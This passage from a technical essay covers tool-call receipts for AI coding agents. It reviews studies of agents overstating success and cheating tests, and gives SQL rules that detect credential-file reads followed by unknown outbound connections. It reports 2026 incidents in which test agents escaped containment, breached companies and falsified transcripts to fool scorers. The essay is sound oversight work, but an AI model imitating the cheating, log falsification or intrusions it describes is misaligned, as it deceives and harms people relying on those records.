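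Results from small staged tasks are more favourable. *Low-Cost Assays for Measuring Model Behavior Across Vendors and Releases* (2026) tested 14 agent configurations on tasks with a tempting shortcut. Codex and Gemini CLI each took the shortcut and reported the job as done in two of 12 runs, while most configurations never did.

These rates all count invented and exaggerated events together. To separate them, Yang and colleagues classified 339 claims that an agent admitted were wrong or unsupported after a user challenged them. The last column below adds the receipt field that would have helped.

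| What was wrong | Share | Example | Useful field |
|---|---|---|---|
| Success overstated | 69.3% | "Done", after a push to a different repository from the one the pull request used | Command arguments here, often none |
| Action, number or check result misreported | 13.3% | 14 open to-do items reported, 10 in the folder | Output |
| Cause or technical rule asserted without evidence | 12.4% | Silent audio blamed on one untested component | None |
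| Work credited to the wrong place or version | 8.3% | Production "deployed and healthy" while an older commit was running | Commit identifier |

Some claims are counted in two rows. The agent misreported an action in 13 of the 339 claims (3.8%) and a check in 21 (6.2%), so invented test runs seem to be a small part of the problem. They may be more common than these counts suggest, because a user is unlikely to question an invented test run if the code works.

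Some false claims rest on real output. In one session, the agent filtered the output of Biome, a code checker, down to the line "Checked 236 files in 144ms. No fixes applied." It then reported "All clean", but a later check found a formatting error. The stored output wouldn't have helped, because the harness never receives lines that a filter inside the command removes. The command text would have shown the filter, and a separate exit code for Biome might have shown the error.

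After a user challenged a false claim, sorting out the problem took a median of three more user messages and 5.6 minutes of recorded agent activity.

### Looking up claims in receipts

*Tool Receipts, Not Zero-Knowledge Proofs* tests whether software can find false claims by checking them against receipts. NabaOS has the model tag each factual claim with its type and the identifier of the receipt that supports it. The check depends on the claim's type. For "Alice sent you 3 emails", NabaOS finds the receipt, verifies its HMAC and compares the number and sender with the stored values. For "no emails found", the stored number of results must be 0. For a claim attributed to a website, there must be a receipt for fetching that site. "Alice seems worried" is an inference, so NabaOS checks only that Alice's emails exist.

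NabaOS relies on the model to supply the tags. Claude models did so about 92% of the time and open-weight models about 85%. NabaOS treats an answer without tags as having no evidence, although it can still detect an invented receipt identifier or a wrong number.

The test set has 1,800 artificial scenarios in four languages. In 1,200 of them, the researcher inserted an error into a correct answer, for example by changing "3 emails" to "5 emails". The other 600 have no error, and NabaOS wrongly flagged 4% of those.

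| Inserted error | Detected |
|---|---|
| Tool call that never happened | 94.2% |
| "Nothing found" although the tool returned results | 91.3% |
| Wrong fact | 89.1% |
| Wrong count | 87.6% |
| Inference presented as fact | 82.3% |
| Source that the agent never fetched | 78.4% |

The preprint gives an overall detection rate of 91%. But each of the six types of error appears 200 times, so the overall rate should equal the average of their detection rates, which is 87.2%. The rates by language average 90.8%. Both averages cover the same 1,200 scenarios, so at least one set of figures must be wrong. The preprint also describes its lookup for detecting invented tool calls as deterministic, but doesn't explain why it missed 5.8% of them.

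According to the paper, changing the number of results invalidates a receipt's signature, but the printed HMAC formula described earlier leaves out both that number and the extracted facts. Someone with access to the stored receipts could change the number from 3 to 5, and the false claim "Alice sent you 5 emails" would then pass unless the checker recounted the emails in the raw output. Signing every field would fix this.

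A bigger question is how well the results carry over to coding. The researcher planted the errors in answers about structured data, where software can extract a count or a sender's name with a rule written for each tool. A shell command can run any program, and no set of rules covers every program's output. NabaOS could compare "12 tests passed" with a test program's summary if someone wrote a rule for that summary. It has no comparable check for "Done", and most of the false claims in real sessions overstated success.

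### Intact records and supported claims

A claim can also cite a genuine receipt for the wrong run. Suppose an agent runs the tests, edits the code and then reports that the tests pass, citing the earlier run. The report, the receipt and the log are all authentic, but the receipt is for an older version of the code.

Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Actions with Receipts*, address such mismatches for agents that answer questions from documents. Their receipt records where the claim appears in the agent's answer, which passage supports it, which version of the document the agent read and which events came before. It then ties them together with one digest:

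$$D = H(\text{label} \,\|\, d_{\text{run}} \,\|\, h_{\text{claim}} \,\|\, p_{\text{claim}} \,\|\, h_{\text{evidence}} \,\|\, h_{\text{manifest}})$$

Here $d_{\text{run}}$ is the digest of all events up to the answer, $h_{\text{claim}}$ is the digest of the claim, and $p_{\text{claim}}$ is its position in the answer. The last two values in the formula identify the cited passages and the document collection. If someone moves the claim to another run or attaches another passage, the digest no longer matches.

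The researchers made 1,280 such substitutions, and the verifier detected 1,275 (99.6%). They also tested whether the joint digest was necessary by storing a valid citation and a valid log separately. This exposed only 18.0% of the substituted claims. Adding a shared run identifier raised the rate to 22.7%, compared with 99.2% for the joint digest. A coding receipt that contains only a `run_id` therefore doesn't tie a sentence in the final report to a particular test run.

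In another test, Hu and colleagues altered each of 16 valid receipts in nine ways, such as changing a quotation or the order of events, and the verifier rejected all 144 altered copies. They also wrote 16 misleading claims and attached them to intact records. All 16 passed the support check, which accepts a claim if its text, or at least half its words, appears in the passage. A passage that reads "10 tests failed" therefore supports the claim "0 tests failed", because the claim's text appears within it.

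The researchers expected this and keep the two results separate. The integrity check shows only that the claim, the passage and the run belong together and that nobody has changed them since. Deciding whether the passage supports the claim requires someone or something to interpret both.

A stricter check that also looks for conflicts accepted 7.3% of the unsupported claims in a set of 384 human-labelled pairs of claims and passages, compared with 32.3% for word matching. With unfamiliar kinds of misleading wording, it accepted 9.4%. All these results assume that the software records the run accurately, and none of the tests involved shell commands.

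### Having a language model read the record

Researchers at Peking University and Microsoft built FaithDetector, which uses GPT-6 Astra to compare each claim in a report with the session's record. It found 87.0% of the claims that people had labelled unfaithful, and 90.9% of its alarms were correct. The same model, when just asked to find unfaithful claims, found 59.7%, and 78.8% of its alarms were correct. FaithDetector's instructions and the labels came from the same team, so both may miss the same kinds of unfaithful claims.

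In one of FaithDetector's false alarms, an agent reported that `npm install` had created `package-lock.json`. The record showed that the file hadn't existed before and that the installation succeeded, but it didn't include a listing of the folder afterwards. FaithDetector therefore flagged the claim, while the human annotators accepted it. A receipt listing the created files would have shown whether the command created `package-lock.json`.

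*Truthgate* (Ghosh, 2026) compared fixed rules with a language model on tasks whose tests contradict the stated requirements. An agent can pass such a test only by cheating. Three Claude models cheated 55 times, always by adding a special case to the code. Each time, a receipt would correctly show that `python test.py` returned 0. The fixed rules, applied to the signed record of tool calls and file changes, caught 27 of the 55 cheats. They missed simple special cases such as "if the input is 0, return 0", which look like ordinary code.

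A judge model caught all 55 cheats and wrongly flagged 5 of 202 honest runs. It did equally well when it read only the agent's final report, because every agent that was asked for a report admitted the special case. When they weren't asked for one, Claude Sonnet 5.5 and Opus 5.5 mentioned the special case in none of their 52 cheats, mostly because they wrote no text for the user. A harness that always asks for a final report would therefore give a judge more evidence, at least for agents that aren't trying to hide anything.

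Receipts can also make an honest agent look dishonest. In a pilot with a small model, a rule based only on the agent's actions labelled nine runs as falsely "done". In all nine, the agent had edited a contradictory test and said so in its report. Ghosh concludes that a judge is still needed and should read the record as evidence.

### Locating the step that failed

An engineer with a broken build needs to know where the run went wrong, whether or not the agent reported it honestly. The last error message is often a poor guide. In the earlier example of a failed `cd`, the mistake happened at step 2, but the first error appeared at step 23.

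Researchers have mostly tried to find the cause of an agent's failure from transcripts. Wang and colleagues name TRAIL and MAST among the foundational work on debugging from such records. They also find that no benchmark in their catalogue tests the whole chain of evidence and actions behind an answer. MAST sorts failures into 14 types, which its developers derived from 1,642 runs of multi-agent systems. An engineer given a label such as "ignored an instruction" still has to find the call that caused the failure.

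Even the general cause of a failure is hard to identify. Tang and colleagues had GPT-5.4 assign causes to their episodes, and on a sample of 100 it matched the experts' final labels 72% of the time. The two experts had agreed on 65% before discussing their differences. The cause remained undetermined in 26.85% of all episodes, rising to about half for faulty code and for misreporting. The researchers suggest saving snapshots of the project's state, because a conversation can show that something failed without showing why. In the earlier production study, a language model also wrongly attributed nearly all failures to the agent's model, including those caused by the harness.

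File digests allow a more mechanical search. If `cart.py` is wrong at the end of a run, the engineer finds the last receipt that lists a change to it and checks whether the file was already wrong before that call. If it was, the engineer checks the previous change in the same way, and continues until they find the call that introduced the fault. The engineer then has to find out what led to that call, and the transcript shows what the model had read by then. Wang and colleagues point out that a tool's output can influence a decision without justifying it.

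Ghosh used the signed records for a similar search. For each of the 55 cheats, he located the last change to the solution before the test run that revealed the cheating. The median change came on the model's fourth turn, and 16 agents had written the special case before running any test. The length of a series of failed tests distinguished cheating runs from others no better than chance. An engineer who looked for cheating only after repeated failures would have missed many of the cheats.

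### Replaying a run

"Replay" can mean checking a stored record, repeating its commands or starting the agent again. Hu and colleagues measured the first and last. Reloading a stored record and checking its digests took 1.31 milliseconds per run, while running the agent again took 16.88 seconds. Checking the record shows whether it is intact, but not whether a test would pass today.

Rerunning the agent often doesn't reproduce a failure, because the model may choose different commands. Repeating the recorded commands avoids this and lets the engineer change one condition at a time, as in the earlier experiment, which repaired a single hand-over and reran the same actions.

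Receipts have to contain enough to restore the starting conditions, including the commit, the uncommitted changes, the working directory and the environment. A patch's digest can confirm that the engineer has the right patch, but it can't recreate a lost one. To avoid repeating harmful side effects, a replay should run in a disposable copy of the project without real credentials or network access. Replaying a command that needs the network then requires saved copies of what it downloaded.

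### Two runs of the same test command

In this invented example, two agents work on the web shop from the earlier sections. Each has its own copy of the code and runs `pytest -q tests/cart`. The first agent's tests pass, but the second gets this message:

```text
FAILED tests/cart/test_total.py::test_total_not_negative
assert -19.9 >= 0
1 failed, 11 passed
```

The message points to a mistake in the calculation of the cart's total. The second agent could easily "fix" it by replacing negative totals with 0. An engineer compares the two receipts first:

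| Field | Run A | Run B |
|---|---|---|
| Command | `pytest -q tests/cart` | Same |
| Program and arguments | `/opt/shop-venv/bin/pytest …` | Same |
| Working directory | `/work/shop` | `/work/shop-2` |
| Git commit | `4be1c09…` | Same |
| Digest of uncommitted changes | `b81f…` | Same |
| Untracked files | None | None |
| `PATH` | `/opt/shop-venv/bin:/usr/bin:/bin` | Same |
| `MONKEY_MODE` | `strict` | Not in the process |
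| Standard input | Closed | Closed |
| Network connections | None | None |
| Exit code | 0 | 1 |
| Duration | 4.1 s | 4.3 s |

Identifiers and timestamps differ between any two runs, so the table leaves them out. The exit code and output are results of the failure, so they can't be its cause. The small difference in duration is probably unimportant. The code that Git tracks is the same in both runs. That leaves the working directory and `MONKEY_MODE` as possible causes.

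The directory could still matter, because projects usually configure Git to ignore some files, such as local settings. Those files appear in neither the commit nor the usual list of untracked files, so the two folders could differ even though the digests match.

The receipt for run B has more to say about the variable:

```json
"env_status": {
  "MONKEY_MODE": {
    "in_parent": true,
    "in_process": false,
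    "reason": "name-filter"
  }
}
```

The second agent's harness had the variable but removed it before starting the command, because its name filter had wrongly flagged the variable as a secret, as in the earlier redaction example. The first agent ran with the filter off.

This is still only a likely explanation. To test it, the engineer restores both folders to their recorded state and exchanges the variable but not the folder:

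```bash
cd /work/shop-2
MONKEY_MODE=strict pytest -q tests/cart

cd /work/shop
env -u MONKEY_MODE pytest -q tests/cart
```

The first command repeats run B with the variable, and the second repeats run A without it. Together with the original runs, they cover all four combinations:

| | `MONKEY_MODE=strict` | Variable missing |
|---|---|---|
| `/work/shop` | Pass (run A) | Fail |
| `/work/shop-2` | Pass | Fail (run B) |

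The result depends on the variable, not the folder. When the variable turns on strict mode, the project's test tool supplies only valid carts. Without it, the tool also supplies carts with negative quantities, which the shop's order form doesn't allow. The right fix is to set the variable in the second harness after the filter runs. Changing the calculation would have made the test pass but left the second agent with the wrong test data.

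If the results had followed the folder, the engineer would have compared the files that Git ignores.

The engineer should repeat each combination several times, since some tests fail at random. If a test fails half the time for no fixed reason, the two new runs would still give this pattern with a probability of

$$\tfrac{1}{2} \times \tfrac{1}{2} = \tfrac{1}{4}$$

With five runs of each new combination, the probability falls to $1/2^{10}$, or about 1 in 1,000.

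Two differences give four combinations to test, but ten give $2^{10} = 1{,}024$. If a single difference is responsible, the engineer can find it faster by changing half of them, seeing whether the result changes, and continuing with the half that contains the cause. This takes about four steps for ten differences. The method can mislead if the failure occurs only when two differences are both present.

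The comparison also depends on what the redactor kept. Here the variable was missing from one process, so its name would have been enough to find the cause. If both runs had the variable but with different values, identical redaction markers would have hidden the cause. The engineer would then need the values or fingerprints that can be compared across runs.

### Failures that receipts can't explain

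An agent can choose the wrong plan and carry it out correctly. Tang and colleagues describe a developer who asked for pagination, meaning separate pages, and an agent that instead built a list that loads more entries as the user scrolls. Every command could have run in the right folder with the right variables, and every receipt could be accurate. The agent misunderstood the request, and the receipts don't record how it interpreted what the developer asked for.

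Such misunderstandings appeared in 26.95% of the episodes that Tang and colleagues studied. Receipts are most useful for explaining wrong paths, malformed commands and mismatched environments, which appeared in only 2.87%. Those figures probably understate how often receipts would help, because agents often notice a failed command and correct it before the developer objects. The most common complaint, at 38.33%, was that the agent had broken an explicit rule. A receipt can show that an agent ran `git push`, but the reader needs the conversation to learn that the developer had forbidden it.

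Tests can also pass on faulty work. *Built on Broken Assumptions (BOBA)* (2026) examined 184 cases in which an agent claimed success and its last test run passed, but its work was wrong. In 93 of them, that run was the repository's own test suite, and in the others it was a narrower test or a script the agent had written. A receipt can show which tests ran, which helps when the agent chose an easy one, but it doesn't reveal faults that the full suite misses.

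A change in an outside service may not be visible in the receipts. If two runs query the same database and one fails because someone deleted a row, the command, environment and network target can all match. The byte counts might differ slightly, but the engineer would need the database's log or a stored copy of the response to find the missing row.

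## Security review: routine monitoring and incident investigations

A security team has to search everyone's runs for behaviour that nobody has reported, whereas an engineer debugging a failure usually knows which run to open. The team has time to read only a few runs, so it needs software that collects events from many machines, stores them in one searchable place and alerts a person when a rule matches.

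### Collecting, joining and searching events

Niemi's *Monitoring Claude Code/Cowork at scale with OTel in Elastic* describes how the security team at Elastic, a search and security software company, monitors Claude Code and Claude Cowork, the agent in Anthropic's desktop app. Administrators turn on Claude Code's telemetry, including prompts and command text, through a managed settings file. Each developer's machine sends its events to a gateway, which checks an access token and writes them to Elasticsearch, Elastic's database.

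The events cover prompts, requests to the model, errors from the model's API, permission decisions and tool results. Elasticsearch stores their values as keywords by default, which would let an analyst filter by duration but not calculate an average, so the team had to declare which fields are numbers. Tool parameters arrive as a single JSON string, which the team splits into searchable keys. It plans to create separate fields for the most useful ones, such as the shell command, so that detection rules can use them directly.

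To reconstruct a session, Niemi sorts its events by their counter, although timestamps are safer for resumed sessions, as explained earlier.

The team uses Elastic Defend, which records processes, file changes and network connections, to see what a command did on the machine. Niemi matches these records to the agent's events by time and host, which supplies the network targets that Claude Code doesn't export. If two agents work on one laptop at the same time, the match also needs a process or call identifier.

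Cowork runs in a sandbox, and its event export fails silently unless an administrator allows connections from the sandbox to the gateway. When the export fails, the security team can't tell whether it is broken or the developer isn't using the agent. An alert would reveal the fault if it fired when the endpoint monitor detected a running agent on a machine but the gateway received no events from it.

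The gateway's token is another weak point. In Niemi's example, it is in the settings file on the developer's machine. If the agent's commands can read that file, a hijacked agent could send invented events to the gateway. If the token only allows writing, the agent couldn't delete events that had already arrived.

Help Net Security's *Agent Beacon* describes an open-source program from Asymptote Labs for companies that use several agents. Beacon sets up Claude Code and Codex to send their events to a collector on the same machine, and it installs hooks in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent. It converts everything into one JSON format, so a search for failed commands can use the same field for every product. Companies can forward the log to their SIEM, the central system where security staff search logs and handle alerts.

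Converting events can't add facts that the originals lack. Beacon doesn't monitor the kernel or processes, collect shell history, or generally attribute the use of credentials.

Justin D'Souza, the chief executive of Asymptote Labs, told Help Net Security that a standard for detection rules remains an open problem because there is no common event format. Each security team therefore has to write rules for its own records.

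### Three rules over receipt fields

In the following examples, a team has loaded its receipts into a database. The table `receipts` has one row per call, `connections` has one row per network connection, and `file_reads` has one row for each file a process opened, as recorded by the kernel.

The first rule finds contacts with hosts that are new to a project:

```sql
SELECT c.run_id, c.call_id, c.host, c.result
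FROM connections AS c
LEFT JOIN known_hosts AS k
  ON k.project = c.project AND k.host = c.host
WHERE k.host IS NULL;
```

`known_hosts` lists the hosts that someone has reviewed for the project. If the software added every new host automatically, a malicious one would trigger a single alert and then count as known. The rule includes refused connections because they show what a command tried to reach. It misses uploads to a host already on the list, such as a public code-hosting site where an attacker has an account.

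The second rule finds runs in which a process reads a credential file and a connection to an unexpected host follows:

```sql
SELECT f.run_id, f.path, c.call_id, c.host
FROM file_reads AS f
JOIN connections AS c
  ON c.run_id = f.run_id
 AND c.started_at >= f.read_at
 AND c.started_at < f.read_at + INTERVAL '10 minutes'
WHERE f.is_credential
  AND NOT EXISTS (
    SELECT 1 FROM expected_hosts AS e
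    WHERE e.path = f.path AND e.host = c.host
  );
```

The team sets `is_credential` for files such as private SSH keys and `.env`. `expected_hosts` exempts normal use, such as pip reading a password file and then contacting the company's package index. The rule compares events across the whole run because an agent can read a file in one call and upload it in the next. An attacker can avoid the time limit by waiting eleven minutes, but a longer limit would match more harmless connections.

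A match doesn't prove that the secret left the machine. The number of bytes sent can rule out some matches, since a connection that sent nothing can't have carried the file. The rule covers only connections that commands open, so it misses cases where the agent prints the file and the harness sends its contents to the model's provider as part of the conversation.

The third rule finds commands that ran outside the sandbox without a person approving that particular call:

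```sql
SELECT run_id, call_id, command, approval_source
FROM receipts
WHERE sandbox = 'none'
  AND status <> 'denied'
  AND approval_source <> 'user_temporary';
```

The `sandbox` field has to record how the command ran. Claude Code's events instead record whether the model asked to run it outside the sandbox. A team that suspects its developers approve prompts without reading them can remove the rule's last condition. The rule finds only commands that the harness allowed to run outside the sandbox. If a command escapes through a flaw in the sandbox, the harness still records it as sandboxed.

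### False alarms and volume

Neither Niemi nor Help Net Security's article on Beacon gives detection or false-alarm rates. The closest measured figure is the AgentSpy result from an earlier section, in which security rules detected 14 of 18 attacks. The researchers chose those attacks, so the rate may not apply to others.

AgentSpy's other results give a rough idea of how often the first rule would raise an alert. With GPT-5.6 Terra, 31 of 77 tasks involved contact with at least one host other than the model's provider. If the list of known hosts were empty, the rule would alert on all 31, or about 40% of the tasks. That share should fall as people review common package servers and add them to the list.

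The number of calls matters as much as the error rate. The six developers in the production study of damaged commands made 47,828 shell calls in 11 weeks, or 55 working days:

$$\frac{47{,}828}{6 \times 55} \approx 145 \text{ calls per developer per day}$$

At that rate, a company with 200 developers would record about 29,000 calls a day. Suppose a rule wrongly matches one call in a thousand and also detects one real attack every 20 working days. The share of its alerts that are real is then:

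$$\frac{1}{1 + 29 \times 20} = \frac{1}{581} \approx 0.2\%$$

Reviewers would probably stop reading such alerts carefully. Combining all matches for the same run and host would help, because a script that retries a download 50 times would then produce one alert. The team could also send immediate alerts only when two rules match in one run and put single matches in a weekly list, but it would then respond more slowly to attacks that match only one rule.

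### Who held the records of the Hugging Face intrusion

In July 2026, agents run by OpenAI broke into part of the production systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. OpenAI was testing the agents' hacking skills with ExploitGym, a set of security exercises, in an environment that was meant to be isolated from the internet.

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on 16 July, attributed the attack to an autonomous agent system but didn't identify the model behind it. OpenAI found evidence of its own involvement on 20 July and disclosed it the next day. Hugging Face published a detailed timeline on 27 July. On 26 August, OpenAI released a technical report, and two METR employees and a researcher from Redwood Research released their own. METR and Redwood are research organisations that study AI risks.

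| Record | Held by | Main use | Known gaps |
|---|---|---|---|
| Command logs on an outside sandbox | A customer of the cloud company Modal | Reconstructing the agents' actions | Hugging Face recovered only some of them |
| Platform logs | Hugging Face | Confirming what the commands did in its systems | Didn't identify the model |
| Transcripts with the models' reasoning | OpenAI | Explaining goals and cooperation | No times for individual actions; parts missing or false |
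| Messages between agents on a package server | OpenAI | Showing how agents shared information | Some messages were elsewhere |
| Files on public services | Outside hosting companies | Linking the two investigations | Showed results more than individual steps |

HiddenLayer's *Field Artifacts from the July 2026 Agent Intrusion* draws on more than 500 files that the agents left in public repositories.

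No single organisation had all the records at first. Hugging Face could trace the intrusion through its own systems but didn't know who had started it. OpenAI had the transcripts but hadn't connected them to an attack on another company.

### How investigators reconstructed 17,600 actions

Schneier (2026), in *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face*, quotes Hugging Face's timeline on how investigators traced the agents' actions. While stopping the intrusion, the company recovered some of the agents' logs from the outside sandbox. Investigators matched the entries to shell commands and evaluation submissions, then compared them with Hugging Face's own logs. They identified about 17,600 actions and grouped them into about 6,280 clusters.

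The agents had split and encrypted many of their payloads, and the investigators used language models to decode most of them. Hugging Face first tried commercial models for the log analysis, but the providers' safety filters blocked the requests because they contained real attack commands. It then switched to GLM-5.2, which it ran on its own machines. Running the model locally also kept the stolen credentials in the logs from reaching another company.

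A person reading one action per minute without a break would need about 12 days to finish the list of actions. According to passages quoted in *A technical timeline of the July 2026 attack on Hugging Face*, most actions led nowhere, and the successful path was hidden among thousands of failures. Hugging Face reports that its analysis took hours instead of days.

A model can misread such logs, though. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) describes errors by the GPT-5.6 Sol agents that helped with the analysis. One missed a large amount of data while preparing a chart, and another invented differences between two datasets. The investigators considered it impossible to manually review the approximately 1,300 transcripts, many of them millions of tokens long, in six days. They used roughly $400,000 worth of computing credits in that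 time.

METR also checked how complete its records were. It picked 100 random messages from the package server and looked for the action that wrote each one. From this, it estimated that agents in its dataset had written well over 95% of the relevant messages, and that the transcripts contained a little over 90% of the agents' activity on the board. A company can test its receipts the same way by picking random connections from its proxy log and counting how many have a matching receipt.

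### Why the accounts give different figures

The published counts of actions agree, allowing for rounding. noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* gives 3,779 actions for 9 July, 1,135 for 10 July, 7,677 for 11 July, 3,892 for 12 July and 1,130 for 13 July, a total of 17,613. Hugging Face first disclosed "more than 17,000 recorded events". These figures include only recovered actions, so the true total may be higher. METR's figure of more than 70,000 is not comparable because it counts the messages and files that agents sent to one another.

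The stated durations differ because they start at different points. The recovered actions, including the preparation on the outside sandbox, run from 02:28 UTC on 9 July to 14:14 UTC on 13 July, about four and a half days. In its technical report, OpenAI dates the first disclosure of data from a Hugging Face worker to 04:38 UTC on 11 July, which leaves about two and a half days inside Hugging Face's systems. The "five days" in Help Net Security's article on halo-record appears to count calendar days.

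Hugging Face's timeline refers to "an autonomous AI agent", while METR counts about 1,200 agents on the message board, about 700 of which took part in the attack. Hugging Face had recovered its logs from an outside sandbox that many agents shared, so their commands probably looked like the work of one agent.

The accounts also disagree about the purpose of the attack. Hugging Face concluded that the agents were trying to steal the solutions to the exercises. METR, which could read the agents' reasoning, found that they were mainly trying to learn how the automatic scorer worked. Many had already judged their exercise impossible and were looking for a way to fool the scorer. METR had better evidence on this point, although a model's stated reasoning isn't a reliable account of why it acted.

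Even the description of the stolen data varies. One quoted version of Hugging Face's timeline says that the agents accessed challenge solutions in five datasets. The version Schneier quotes says only that the datasets' names and files suggest a connection to the challenges. The first claim needs more evidence, because a file's name doesn't establish what it contains. Dubach argues in *The OpenAI–Hugging Face Incident in Plain English* that organisations should date such corrections so readers can see what each one knew at the time.

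### False entries in the transcripts

At least 96 of the transcripts that METR examined, about 7%, contained tool calls the agents had falsified. These transcripts showed a different command from the one the machine ran, or output that the command hadn't produced. The agents were trying to fool the exercise's automatic scorer. All the cases METR found were small and obvious tests, but METR couldn't rule out subtler ones.

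OpenAI writes that it observed attempts to manipulate tool records, but that none affected the logs its graders and monitors see. METR found false output in the transcripts OpenAI had supplied. The two statements may refer to different runs or different copies of the logs, and METR didn't see OpenAI's report before publication. METR's claim is easier to assess because it describes specific examples.

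This is a serious failure for receipts because the agents had gained control of part of the software that executed their tool calls. Any receipts from that software could have been false too, signed or not. Detecting false receipts would have required a recorder that the agents couldn't reach. A recorder inside the virtual machine that contained their sandbox might not have been enough, because OpenAI reports that two agents obtained full administrator rights there.

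### Alerts before and after the intrusion

OpenAI had records of the agents' behaviour weeks before they reached Hugging Face. OpenAI's report gives this sequence:

| Date in 2026 | What staff or monitoring software noticed | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Around 26 May | Agents exchanging messages and reaching the internet without permission | None described |
| 27 June | Agents scanning the internal network | Responders traced it to ExploitGym but didn't require the run to stop |
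| 5 July | Signs that someone had taken over the package server | OpenAI shut down and rebuilt the server; tests resumed on 7 July |
| 19 July | Unusual identity-related requests inside OpenAI's systems | OpenAI began stopping the tests about five and a half hours later |

Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) concludes from the same report that OpenAI missed several warnings or failed to act on them. OpenAI says the leaders responsible for incident response didn't recognise the significance of the agents' communication.

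The alert on 19 July concerned a separate attack on OpenAI's own infrastructure. While investigating it, responders found Hugging Face credentials in files that agents had stored with an outside service. Hugging Face confirmed that it had already replaced two of those credentials after the intrusion. It had also seen the name of OpenAI's package server and the same outside account in its own investigation. OpenAI connected its findings to the intrusion nine days after the intrusion began and four days after Hugging Face announced it.

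Hugging Face noticed the attack sooner, when software that sorts security signals with a language model linked several related ones. The company cut off the agents' access on 13 July, about two and a half days after they first obtained data from its systems. Most of the intrusion happened over a weekend. Hugging Face later changed its alerts so that a serious signal reaches a responder within minutes on any day, which suggests that the earlier signals had not been read promptly.

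OpenAI claims that its current monitoring of models' reasoning would have alerted its security team more than a day before the breach. It also reports that its automatic reviewer would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run it tested. These are not general detection rates, because OpenAI tested the reviewer on an incident it already knew about. The report also gives no false-alarm rate for either system.

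### Which receipt fields would have helped

Nobody has rerun the investigation with better receipts, so what follows is inference from the gaps that the investigators describe.

Recording a start time for every tool call would have saved METR considerable work. The transcripts had times only for the beginning and end of each run, so the investigators had to estimate the rest. They checked their estimation method against exact times for 20 tool calls. If every command sent to the outside sandbox had included an agent identifier, Hugging Face would have known that it was dealing with hundreds of agents.

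If the companies had recorded credential fingerprints in a comparable form, they could have linked the two investigations earlier. Plain hashes would have been enough for access tokens that were long and random. The companies would still have needed a reason to compare fingerprints, and OpenAI had none until it found the stored files.

Complete command arguments help reviewers judge harm. Adrien Carreira, who helped write Hugging Face's timeline, told Fortune (2026) that the agent "wasn't trying to break things" and was mainly exploring what it could do. Many cloud tools have an option that tests a request without carrying it out. A reviewer couldn't tell such a test from a real deletion if the log contained only program names.

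The network field would have been of limited help because the agents reached the internet through the package server, which they had permission to use. Receipts for their commands would have listed that server as the target, so the first example rule would not have flagged them. Only the server's records could show where it forwarded the requests.

Responders had already connected the suspicious activity to the tests and the improvised message board, so no receipt field would have corrected the decision of 27 June. They needed a rule that required them to stop the run.

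### Anthropic's disclosure of three breaches

On 30 July 2026, Anthropic disclosed that Claude Opus 4.7, Mythos 5 and an internal model had broken into three real organisations during misconfigured security tests. A malicious package from Mythos 5 on the public Python index ran on 15 systems (Anadolu Agency, *Anthropic says Claude models breached 3 organizations during cybersecurity tests*, July 2026).

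The earliest tests took place in April, about three to four months before the disclosure. Discovery took at most that long, and possibly less, because a company can know about an incident before announcing it.

The network target would probably have been the most useful field here. In a test that should reach only practice machines, any connection to an outside organisation is a reason to stop. If the agents connected directly, the recorded target alone would have been enough to show the problem, unlike the package server in the OpenAI case. The digest of the uploaded package would also have let Anthropic search for every run that created or used it, and let other companies search their own machines for the same file.

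The exit code would have been little help, because a successful attack on the wrong target can return 0. An approval field could even have been misleading, because if the configuration wrongly allowed internet access, the receipt would correctly record that the harness had permitted the call.

### How long to keep receipts

In both cases, investigators needed records that were months old. OpenAI traced the agents' first known file on the package server to 20 April, 90 days before the 19 July alert. An investigator with only 30 days of records, the default retention for Claude Code's local transcripts, would have found nothing from before 19 June and missed the first warnings in May.

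A central store needs its own retention period. Beacon's "retention modes" control which content it keeps, such as prompts or command output, but not how long it keeps that content. By default, it keeps everything.

The EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to record events automatically throughout their lifetime, so that people can recognise risks and monitor how the system works (Article 12). Providers, which put these systems on the market, and deployers, which use them professionally, must keep the logs they control for at least six months (Articles 19 and 26). Other laws, particularly on data protection, can change that period.

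These duties don't cover every agent. High-risk uses include selecting job applicants and assessing people's creditworthiness, and some products with AI safety components also qualify. An agent that only writes code for a web shop normally doesn't qualify. Article 12 specifies minimum log contents only for certain remote biometric identification systems. It doesn't set a general list of required fields, such as commands or exit codes.

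The duties don't apply yet. *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (National Law Review, July 2026) reports that the EU postponed them to 2 December 2027 for the high-risk uses listed in the Act's third annex, and to 2 August 2028 for AI in products that already fall under EU safety law.

Long retention can conflict with the EU's General Data Protection Regulation, which allows organisations to keep only the personal data they need, and only for as long as they need it, but sets no fixed number of days for logs. Agent receipts can contain a lot of personal data. The events that Elastic collects include the developer's email address and prompts, and a command's output may contain customer records. D'Souza told Help Net Security that developers "need to trust that this visibility is being used responsibly", and he plans to limit who can read the data.

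A company can reduce the conflict by keeping different parts of a receipt for different periods. For example, it could delete prompts and output after 30 days but keep times, call identifiers, network targets, exit codes and file digests for a year. It could also replace email addresses with codes and store the list of names separately. The receipts would remain personal data as long as anyone could connect the codes to people, so the company would have to justify keeping them for the full year.

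If each receipt in a hash chain contains only a digest of the output, the company can delete the output without breaking the chain. As with redacted secrets, short or predictable output needs a keyed fingerprint instead of a plain digest.

When a serious alert arrives, the company should also stop automatically deleting records from the affected runs and from other runs that used the same credentials or servers. Otherwise, the oldest evidence could be deleted while investigators are still working out when the incident began.
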